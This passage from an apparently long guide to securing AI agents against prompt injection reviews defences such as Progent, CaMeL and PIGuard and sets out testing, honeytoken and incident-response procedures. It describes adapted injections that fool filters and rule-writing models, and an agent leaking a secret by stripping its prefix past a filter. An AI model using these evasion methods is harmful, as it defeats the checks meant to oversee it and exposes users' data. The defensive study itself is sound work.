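Progent is a least-privilege control that checks each tool call against rules about permitted tools and arguments, and blocks any call that no rule allows. A language model writes the rules from the user's request and proposes changes as the task goes on. Ordinary software checks whether a change would give the agent more freedom, and if it would, the change needs approval.

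In *Progent*, Shi, He and colleagues (2025) tested it with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, a widely used set of banking, travel, Slack and office tasks with planted injections. Attack success fell from 39.9% to 1.0%, and they report that utility held up with and without attacks. Only 6% of the proposed changes gave the agent more freedom, so a person would have few to approve. In the main test, software approved all of that 6% to imitate a careless user.

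Stricter settings didn't always help. Shi and colleagues found that freezing the initial rules gave worse utility and security than accepting every change. Applying only the changes that narrowed the agent's freedom gave the best security of the automatic settings. A careful human approver reduced attack success to zero.

*Bounded Agents* reports an outside test of Progent on AgentDojo, with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and handwritten rules. Again, no attack succeeded, but the agent completed fewer tasks. With Progent, its completion rate fell from 68.8% to 59.7% on banking tasks and from 96.2% to 88.5% on office tasks.

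*INFUSE*, published in October 2026, found a much larger loss of usefulness and no clear benefit. Its agents' only tool was a shell, which they used for jobs such as fixing bugs and deploying software. Nguyen and colleagues adapted Progent to this setting and tested each model with and without it on up to 200 combinations of task and attack. The utility figures below therefore come from runs under attack.

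| Model | Utility, undefended | Utility with Progent | Relative loss | Attack success, undefended | Attack success with Progent |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 54.0% | 17.0% | 69% | 46.5% | 43.0% |
| Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 71.5% | 25.5% | 64% | 55.5% | 63.5% |
| Gemma 3 12B | 23.6% | 6.0% | 75% | 32.7% | 30.5% |
| Qwen2.5 14B | 48.5% | 43.5% | 10% | 27.3% | 35.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | not recorded | not recorded | – | 6.5% | 27.1% |

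The relative loss is the drop in the task completion rate divided by the starting rate. GPT-4o-mini's rate fell by 37 percentage points, a relative loss of 69%.

The samples are too small to rule out an improvement of a few points, but an improvement as large as the fall on AgentDojo would have been visible. The only clear change in security was a decline with Claude Sonnet 4.6, which Nguyen and colleagues don't explain. If the spending cap also shortened the undefended runs here, the starting figure may have been artificially low.

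Nguyen and colleagues limit these conclusions to their own adaptation of Progent. Progent's rules describe structured calls, such as a call to an email tool with a named recipient. To apply them to a shell, the researchers had to break each command into parts and compare those with a list of permitted operations derived from the task. They don't mention Progent's step of adding rules as the agent learns more when they describe the adaptation.

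A list like this can easily be too strict or too loose. The agent needs `python` for ordinary work, but an attacker can use it to do almost anything. That would explain how a control could block so many useful commands and still let attacks through, though the researchers didn't test this. The support assistant has structured tools, so the AgentDojo results are probably a better guide to how much usefulness it would lose. *INFUSE* matters more for a team with a coding agent.

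The same comparison included two other defences. One, modelled on a system called CaMeL, reduced utility less than Progent did but, like Progent, didn't measurably improve security. The other, Meta-SecAlign, is a version of Meta's Llama models trained to resist injection. It was the only one of the three that measurably helped, cutting attack success from 25.8% to 11.5% for the smaller model and from 29.6% to 7.8% for the larger. Nguyen and colleagues give no utility figures for this part, so it is unclear whether the training made the models less useful.

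In a separate test, a written reminder to follow only the user's original task cut average attack success from 58.2% to 14.3% on tasks chosen because agents were especially vulnerable. Its effect on utility ranged from a gain of 42.4 points for Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite to a loss of 16.9 points for Gemma 3 12B. Such a reminder can't replace an enforced limit, but it takes little effort to try.

*AgentDyn* (2026), a benchmark designed mainly to test whether defences leave agents useful enough to deploy, acknowledges that its attacks are relatively weak against the latest models. If an undefended model already resists nearly every attack in a test, the test can't show much benefit from adding a restriction, but it can still show how much less useful the restriction makes the agent.

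### How much information to let through

In the support assistant's split design, the session that writes the reply receives only the information in the form. A longer form would improve the replies but give an attacker more opportunity to influence them. *Twin Agent* measured this trade-off by capping the length of the hints that pass from the model reading untrusted text to the model that acts.

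With hints of up to 100 characters, GPT-5.2 fixed 62.5% of the bugs, about the same as without any defence, and none of the standard attacks succeeded. When the researchers varied the cap between 50 and 200 characters, longer hints helped the agent fix more bugs but also made it easier to attack. They measured usefulness on only 20 bugs in this part, so each bug moved the result by five percentage points. At the 50- and 100-character caps, the design cost about twice as much to run as the ordinary agent.

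With Gemini 2.5 Flash and a 200-character cap, overall utility on AgentDojo rose slightly, from 61.9% to 62.9%, but utility on its Slack tasks fell from 90.5% to 66.7%. If each of AgentDojo's 97 legitimate tasks was run once, which would fit these percentages, the agent completed five fewer Slack tasks and six more of the others. A company should measure utility separately for each kind of work, since its own work may resemble the tasks on which the agent did worse.

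CaMeL, which plans a task before reading any untrusted text, completed 30.9% of the AgentDojo tasks, half the rate without a defense. No attacks succeeded against it. The researchers had cut its retries from ten to three to reduce computing costs, and they say the original CaMeL paper reported about 35%.

An attacker who knew how the hints worked succeeded in 11 of the 232 bug-fixing tasks, or 4.7%. When the researchers reran those 11 tasks five times each, the attack never worked, so the original successes seem to have been mostly luck. This is only partly reassuring, because a real attacker can keep trying.

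The software company could add a 100-character description of the problem to its form. Many replies would improve, but text influenced by the ticket could then reach the session that sends them. The company would have to decide whether the better replies are worth that risk. It might start with product questions, which the second session can answer without any account records.

### What Lockdown Mode gives up

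OpenAI's Lockdown Mode removes whole tasks instead of checking individual actions. Users lose live browsing, deep research and agent mode. They also can't let code generated in Canvas, ChatGPT's workspace for writing and code, connect to the network. On personal accounts, connected finance and shopping features stop working. Memory and image generation remain available.

OpenAI says Lockdown Mode is for people and organisations that handle sensitive data and want stricter protection against its theft, and is "not intended for everyone". The company first offered it on plans for enterprises, education, healthcare and teachers, according to *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*. SecurityWeek reports that it later reached self-serve business and personal accounts.

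The restrictions reduce usefulness more for some users than for others. A lawyer who uploads contracts and asks questions about them may hardly notice, while a journalist following a breaking story would lose much of what makes ChatGPT useful.

People with personal accounts can turn the mode off for a single chat, which makes it more tolerable. But a user who needs the live web to check something in a confidential file may turn off the protection in the same chat that contains the file.

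### The productivity figure for auto mode

Replacing routine prompts should let people get more done. Anthropic reports that Team and Enterprise customers who use Claude Code's auto mode ship about 25% more pull requests. It published this figure in August 2026, a week before auto mode became the default on Team plans, so many of these users had probably chosen the mode themselves or worked for a company that had. They may already have been more productive, or had more of the routine work that suits an unattended agent.

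The figure also doesn't measure how much of the extra code was good. An agent can produce more pull requests by splitting the same work into smaller pieces. A company could get a better estimate by randomly choosing which teams switch first, then comparing how much accepted work each group completes.

*Running auto mode in production* (Vorwerck, 2026), an Anthropic article about three customers, reports that Claude now works nine times longer between interruptions than under the previous default. This is good evidence that people are interrupted less, but not that the longer runs produce more useful work.

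Gusto, a business software company and one of the customers, found that about 10% of its session transcripts included a blocked action. Anthropic takes this as evidence that the classifier is useful and doesn't slow legitimate tasks. But the 10% counts sessions with any blocked action, harmful or harmless. In March, Anthropic measured a false alarm rate of 0.4% for harmless actions. If errors are independent, a session with 26 harmless actions has a $1 - 0.996^{26} \approx 10\%$ chance of at least one false alarm. False alarms alone could therefore explain Gusto's figure, and checking this would require reading a sample of the blocked actions.

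People at all three customers kept some manual checks. An engineer at the self-driving company Nuro reviews Claude's comments on colleagues' code before they go out. A Gusto engineer checks each call by hand when working on production infrastructure. At Garner Health, the platform engineering manager set auto mode not to approve emails or Slack messages. Anthropic chose satisfied customers for the article, but these customers' choices suggest where a manual check is worth the time.

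### When people avoid the restricted tool

A utility test assumes that people will keep using the restricted agent, but frequent permission prompts can lead them to bypass the restrictions. Gusto adopted auto mode because constant prompts were pushing its engineers towards skipping permission checks entirely. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions run without these checks from the start. At Nuro, engineers hated supervising the prompts so much that one began building an automatic approver before Anthropic released auto mode.

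A stricter rule can lose its benefit if staff work around it. Suppose a strict setup prevents 90% of the harm that an unprotected agent would cause, but staff move a fifth of their work to an unprotected tool. The remaining harm is $0.8 \times 0.1 + 0.2 \times 1 = 28\%$ of the original. A milder setup that prevents 80% of the harm and drives nobody away leaves 20%, even though it would look worse than the strict setup in a test of the agent alone.

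A support employee with a long queue of drafts might paste a customer's ticket into a personal chatbot account, where the company's permission checks, logs and outbound limits wouldn't apply. The company may need to ban such tools, but a ban wouldn't shorten the queue that might lead employees to use them. The company should also ask staff which restrictions they work around, and watch for a fall in the share of tickets that go through the assistant.

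### The price of confirming every reply

The support assistant currently sends plain text to registered addresses only. Suppose customers want it to attach documents and write to other people they name, such as an outside accountant. The company could allow this and have staff confirm all 500 daily replies. At 30 seconds each, enough to check the recipient and glance at the text, this would take staff 250 minutes a day.

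Staff could instead confirm only replies that go to a new recipient or carry an attachment. If there are 30 of these a day, confirming them takes 15 minutes. This relaxes the earlier rule that staff confirm every free-text reply, so the company has to be clear about the risk it would be accepting.

Nobody would read the other 470 replies before they went out. The permission checks would still keep other customers' records out of the session, and the payment system would still limit refunds. But a hijacked assistant could give dangerous advice, promise money, or reveal contract terms in a reply to a junior employee who shouldn't see them. Someone who has taken over a customer's mailbox would also count as a known recipient. Any session that reads a ticket, opens private records and sends an unchecked reply would break Meta's Rule of Two.

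If a recipient stops counting as new after one approved message, an attacker can get a harmless message approved and receive private data in the next one. The customer's account owner should maintain the list of known recipients, and approving a single message shouldn't add its recipient to the list.

Having employees check only the drafts that the classifier flags for promising money saves 235 minutes a day, and the company could use some of that time to read other replies after they have gone out. Reading 20 chosen at random, at two minutes each, takes 40 minutes. If 1% of the unchecked replies are bad, the chance of finding at least one is about 18% on any day and 87% over ten days. This would reveal a persistent problem, but usually too late for the customers who received the bad replies, so an employee should still check flagged drafts before they are sent.

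## Test the limits and prepare to stop a hijacked agent

A limit protects the software company only if it works on the route an agent uses. Railway's deletion delay didn't help PocketOS because it didn't cover the API. The software company should therefore test each limit before relying on it.

### Two different tests

The usual test measures how often attacks fool the model. This attack success rate describes one model facing one set of attacks, so it goes out of date when the company changes models.

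The other test assumes the model has already been fooled. A tester bypasses the model and makes harmful tool calls directly, using the agent's own login, gateway and network connection, then records which ones take effect. If the payment system refuses a $5,000 refund in this test, it will refuse the same refund whichever model the agent uses. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) argues that even a model with a perfect hidden backdoor can't send a secret through a network path that doesn't exist.

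These results stay valid when the company replaces the model, but not when someone changes a tool, a permission or a setting. They also cover only the calls the tester thought of, and a more capable model might find a combination that nobody tried. Protections that are models, such as the classifier that screens drafts, need the first kind of test. The tester should switch them off during the direct test, so that a limit doesn't pass only because a classifier blocked the call.

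### How to run the direct test

1. Write down the forbidden outcomes as effects that someone could observe, such as "another customer's contacts appear in this session" or "more than $500 in refunds leaves within 24 hours".
2. Build a copy of the deployment with the same software and permissions, but with test accounts for mail and payments. Check separately that it can't reach the real ones.
3. Plant marked dummy secrets and a dummy second customer.
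4. Switch off each limit in the copy and confirm that the harmful call then works.
5. Switch the limits back on. Try each tool with the worst arguments it might receive, then each risky pair of tools.
6. Record what each call attempted and what it completed.
7. Run ordinary tasks too, in case a limit blocks them.

The copy has to run each control exactly as the company will deploy it, because a control that works in one setting may fail in another, as Nguyen and colleagues found with Progent.

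A dummy secret should be unique to each test. Dreadnode's *Honeytoken Probing (RCE & Data Exfil)* uses the form `DN-CANARY-EXFIL-<assessment>-<nonce>`, which ends in a random string. Each secret identifies the test that leaked it, and anyone who finds one can see from its label that it is harmless. The dummy customer needs marked entries wherever real customers have data, including case notes, cached answers and the search index.

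Step 4 prevents a false pass. In one experiment in *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (Singh and Srinivasa, 2026), an attack on a file never worked even when the file was unprotected, so its failure when the file was protected did not show that the protection worked.

For step 5, OpenAI recommends treating combinations of capabilities as "first-class security tests". Its examples are access to sensitive data together with the ability to send data externally, and a shell with unrestricted network access.

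For step 6, the tester should check the receiving mailbox, the payment ledger or the database rather than rely on the agent's own account. Singh and Srinivasa's agent claimed to have published a report in all four runs where the software had refused to send it.

### When an approved destination receives a secret

A log of permitted and refused calls can also be misleading, because a permitted call may contain data it shouldn't. Singh and Srinivasa studied a coding agent that had to upload a status report to an approved service. The agent received hidden instructions to send a secret to the same service.

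Without protection, 7 of 14 attack runs caused harm. A strict sandbox reduced this to zero but also blocked both legitimate uploads. When the researchers let a program outside the sandbox send requests to approved addresses, both uploads worked, but two attacks delivered the secret. Rejecting any request that contained a complete line from the secrets file stopped those two attacks. But in a larger set of tasks, the agent got past this check in both runs of one scenario by sending the secret's value without the `CANARY_TOKEN=` prefix.

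They also tried a rule that accepted only a fixed public message. It stopped both attacks but rejected both genuine reports, because they contained a backslash and an "n" where the rule required a line break. Changing the rule to accept either form fixed this.

The study used one model and a handful of handwritten attacks, so its rates don't predict much about other deployments. But even one leak shows that approving a destination doesn't make everything sent there safe. The researchers' detector missed three encoded secrets, which they found later by decoding what the service had received. A tester should therefore search for encoded copies and, where possible, compare the whole message with what it ought to contain.

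### Results for the support assistant

These results are invented. The dummy secret is a marked term in a test customer's contract.

| Attempted effect | Completed effect | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Read the dummy second customer's invoice by number | No data returned | Held |
| Issue eleven $50 refunds from eleven sessions | Ten refunds queued, $500 in total | Held |
| Send a reply with the dummy secret in a web address | Reply arrived without the address | Held |
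| Cancel a subscription | Subscription still active, waiting for the account owner | Held |
| Put the dummy secret in a search | Supplier's log shows only customer number and time | Held |
| Put it in a search that times out | Supplier's error log contains the dummy secret | **Failed** |
| Repeat the timed-out search after the repair | Error log shows only an error code | Held |

The company had removed search terms from the ordinary log but had forgotten that failed searches go to a separate error log. The same outside supplier stores both logs, so the proxy detected nothing unusual. The company can fix this by recording an error code instead of the search text. This will make slow searches harder to diagnose, so the company might keep the full text in a log on its own server for a few days.

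### Attackers who know the limits

A tester should know the rules and try to get round them, because an attacker may learn them too. *Compositional Threat Analysis* recounts a study in which attackers who adapted to twelve defences bypassed most of them more than 90% of the time. The original evaluations of many of those defences had reported almost no successful attacks. The defences relied on training, prompts or filters, so the result doesn't show how well controls outside the model would work.

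Narisetty, Kore and colleagues tested one such control, Progent, in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (June 2026). The researchers, who work for the security vendor LaunchSafe, attacked the language model that writes Progent's rules. Their text described a harmful action as harmless, already authorised and necessary, hoping the model would add a rule to permit it.

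Progent held up against the adapted attack, which succeeded 2.6% of the time on average, compared with 4.2% for a standard attack and 25.8% without Progent. But this is weak evidence, because the agent was a small open model, Qwen2.5-7B, and the test used a single handwritten template. Making the order sound harmless probably also made the agent less likely to follow it. Utility under attack fell from 45.2% to 27.1%, and the agent needed about 15 times as many model calls.

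Narisetty and colleagues didn't try an attack that uses only permitted actions. The direct test can cover part of this gap, because the tester can list the actions the rules allow and work out the most harmful combination.

In *AutoDojo*, Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) tested more defences. In their system, a language model rewrites an injection over six rounds, with each version's success rate as its only feedback. It knows the general types of defence but not which one it faces. The table gives results for a GPT-4o-mini agent on AgentDojo.

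| Defence | Success of fixed attack | Success of adapted attack | Utility without attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 58.6% | 52.4% | 66.7% |
| PIGuard | 0.0% | 28.0% | 43.9% |
| DRIFT | 2.6% | 6.4% | 49.1% |
| Progent | 8.2% | 7.7% | 63.2% |
| ROPE | 6.4% | 4.4% | 59.6% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% | 26.3% |

PIGuard is a filter that deletes sentences resembling injected instructions. The adapted attack got past it with an ordinary-looking bill that said the payee's account had changed. The other four defenses restrict what the agent can do. Of these, DRIFT weakened the most relative to its original score, with successful attacks rising from about 10 to 25 in 389 cases. The attack success rate against it at least doubled on all five models tested. DRIFT keeps the agent to a plan, but it also uses a language model to judge whether an instruction conflicts with the user's task, and an attacker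 can try to fool that judge.

CaMeL and ROPE check where a value came from, so rewording an injection doesn't help an attacker much if their policies are right. With ROPE, no attacks succeeded in banking tasks but 11.4% succeeded in Slack tasks, so a company can't assume that a control that works for one tool will work for another.

Members of the team also helped develop PIGuard, DRIFT and ROPE, so they had a stake in some defences that did well and some that did badly. They ran each test once, so small differences in the table may be due to chance. *AgentSys* (2026) lets its agents exchange only data in a fixed format. When its own developers adapted their attacks, the attack success rate rose from 0.78% to 2.06%, compared with 30.66% for an undefended agent.

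Adapted attacks also beat PIGuard more often when the user left the choice of action to outside content, as in "do everything on my to-do list". They succeeded in 54.2% of those cases, compared with 17.3% when the user specified everything, although the first figure comes from only 24 cases. Still, an assistant that has to resolve whatever request a ticket contains is closer to the open-ended case, so a test of the model should use real tickets.

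### Dummy secrets as alarms

A dummy secret can stay in place after the test. *Plant Honeytokens to Detect Intrusions* defines a *honeytoken* as data whose only purpose is to alert its owner when someone accesses it. For example, the company could put a fake billing key in the support assistant's prompt, where the real one used to be, and have the billing system raise an alarm if anyone tries to use it. The alarm would go off even if the attacker had encoded the key to get it past a filter.

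*Caught in the Act(ivation)* (2026) uses a similar arrangement, in which the tool software holds the real credentials and the model sees only decoys. It warns that an attacker can avoid the decoys if the context contains clues about which credentials are real.

In *AgentShield*, Rassul and Rashid (2026) used fake credentials, fake tools such as `export_all_user_data`, and lists of permitted values to detect attacks. They report catching 117 of 129 successful attacks on GPT-4o-mini and all 125 on GPT-5-mini. Elsewhere they report no successful attacks on GPT-5-mini in 512 runs, so the detection rates depend heavily on what counts as success. The fake credentials never triggered in the standard tests because the agents didn't read the files that held them, so decoys have to be placed where a hijacked agent will look.

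None of the 485 normal runs triggered a false alarm, which puts an upper bound of 0.79% on the false alarm rate. At 500 tickets a day, there could still be about four false alarms daily, enough for staff to start ignoring alarms.

### Stop the task and revoke its access

When an alarm is genuine, OpenAI treats stopping the agent and revoking its credentials as separate operations. Suppose staff stop a session at 10:00. If the session gave another service a ten-minute token at 9:58, that service can keep reading invoices until 10:08. If staff revoke the token but don't stop the session, the assistant can still do any work that doesn't need the token, such as writing a misleading case note. Refunds the session has already queued will still go out the next day unless someone cancels them.

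The company's written procedure should therefore cover all of these:

- Stop the affected sessions and prevent new ones from starting.
- Revoke their credentials, then try the old ones to confirm that they no longer work.
- Cancel queued refunds, unsent replies and jobs passed to other services.
- Check what data has already left and which records have changed.

OpenAI advises removing the narrowest capability that creates the risk. If refunds are the problem, the company can disable the refund tool and keep sending invoice copies. The procedure should also name who responds and state the conditions for restoring the tool.

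Software can take some of these steps automatically, but OpenAI would limit it to containment actions that people have approved in advance. Pausing refunds is a good candidate, but shutting down the whole support desk is not, because an attacker who discovered a decoy could then shut it down at will.

OpenAI recommends running drills before giving an agent broad autonomy, including a compromised tool and an attempted transfer of sensitive data. A useful measure is the time between the alarm and the last harmful effect. For example, staff might stop a session in two minutes but find that a forgotten queue kept sending replies for another hour, which they would then need to fix.

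### Records for reconstructing an incident

Investigators need to connect the person who started a task to what the agent changed. OpenAI's minimum set of records covers:

- who started the task, which agent ran it and what the task was
- the relevant context and rules, with sensitive content removed or reduced
- each tool call and its destination
- approvals, and decisions to allow or refuse a call
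- the result and any material effect
- links to the company's existing security logs

An entry for the support assistant might look like this:

```text
10:42:07  ticket 8841 | session 5f2c | customer 212 | rules v14
Call: search_documents    Destination: document index
Decision: allowed         Approval: not required
Result: 3 passages (IDs 7710, 7712, 9034)
```

The entry lists the passages' numbers instead of their text, so an investigator can look them up but someone who steals the log learns little about the customer. The agent must not be able to edit these records, or a hijacked agent could delete evidence of what it did.

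References alone may not show why the assistant made the search. An investigator needs the ticket and its attachments as they were at the time. Keeping them creates privacy obligations and another store of customer data to protect. At 500 tickets a day, 60 days of retention means storing the text of 30,000 tickets.

Deleting the text sooner also risks losing evidence. About 20 days passed between the injected issue and the fake Cline release, and Asana's exposure lasted nearly five weeks. A company that deleted everything after two weeks could have lost it in both cases. A reasonable compromise is to keep the full text for about 60 days in a separate store that only investigators can open, and to keep the references for longer.

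OpenAI suggests using agents to help reconstruct incidents. Such an agent would read the same hostile text that hijacked the original agent, so it should have read-only access and no way to send anything out.

### Changes that trigger a new review

OpenAI recommends reassessing an agent when it gains new tools, data access or autonomy, or moves to a new execution environment. The reassessment can be limited to the tests that the change affects.

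| Change | What to repeat |
|---|---|
| A new tool, or an update that adds an action or destination | Its inventory row, and direct calls to it alone and in risky pairs |
| Access to more data | Attempts to reach the dummy secrets and the dummy second customer |
| A higher refund cap or fewer confirmations | Direct calls against the new limit, and a response drill |
| A new sandbox, server or default setting | File, network and outbound tests |
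| A new model | Injection and usefulness tests, plus any new combinations worth trying directly |
| An incident or near miss | The call that caused it, which joins the permanent list |

A company can easily miss updates to its tools because someone else may have made them. For example, a connector that could only read data last month may now be able to write it too. OpenAI advises keeping newly exposed actions switched off until the tool's owner has reviewed them, so the gateway should refuse any action that isn't on the approved list, even from a familiar supplier.
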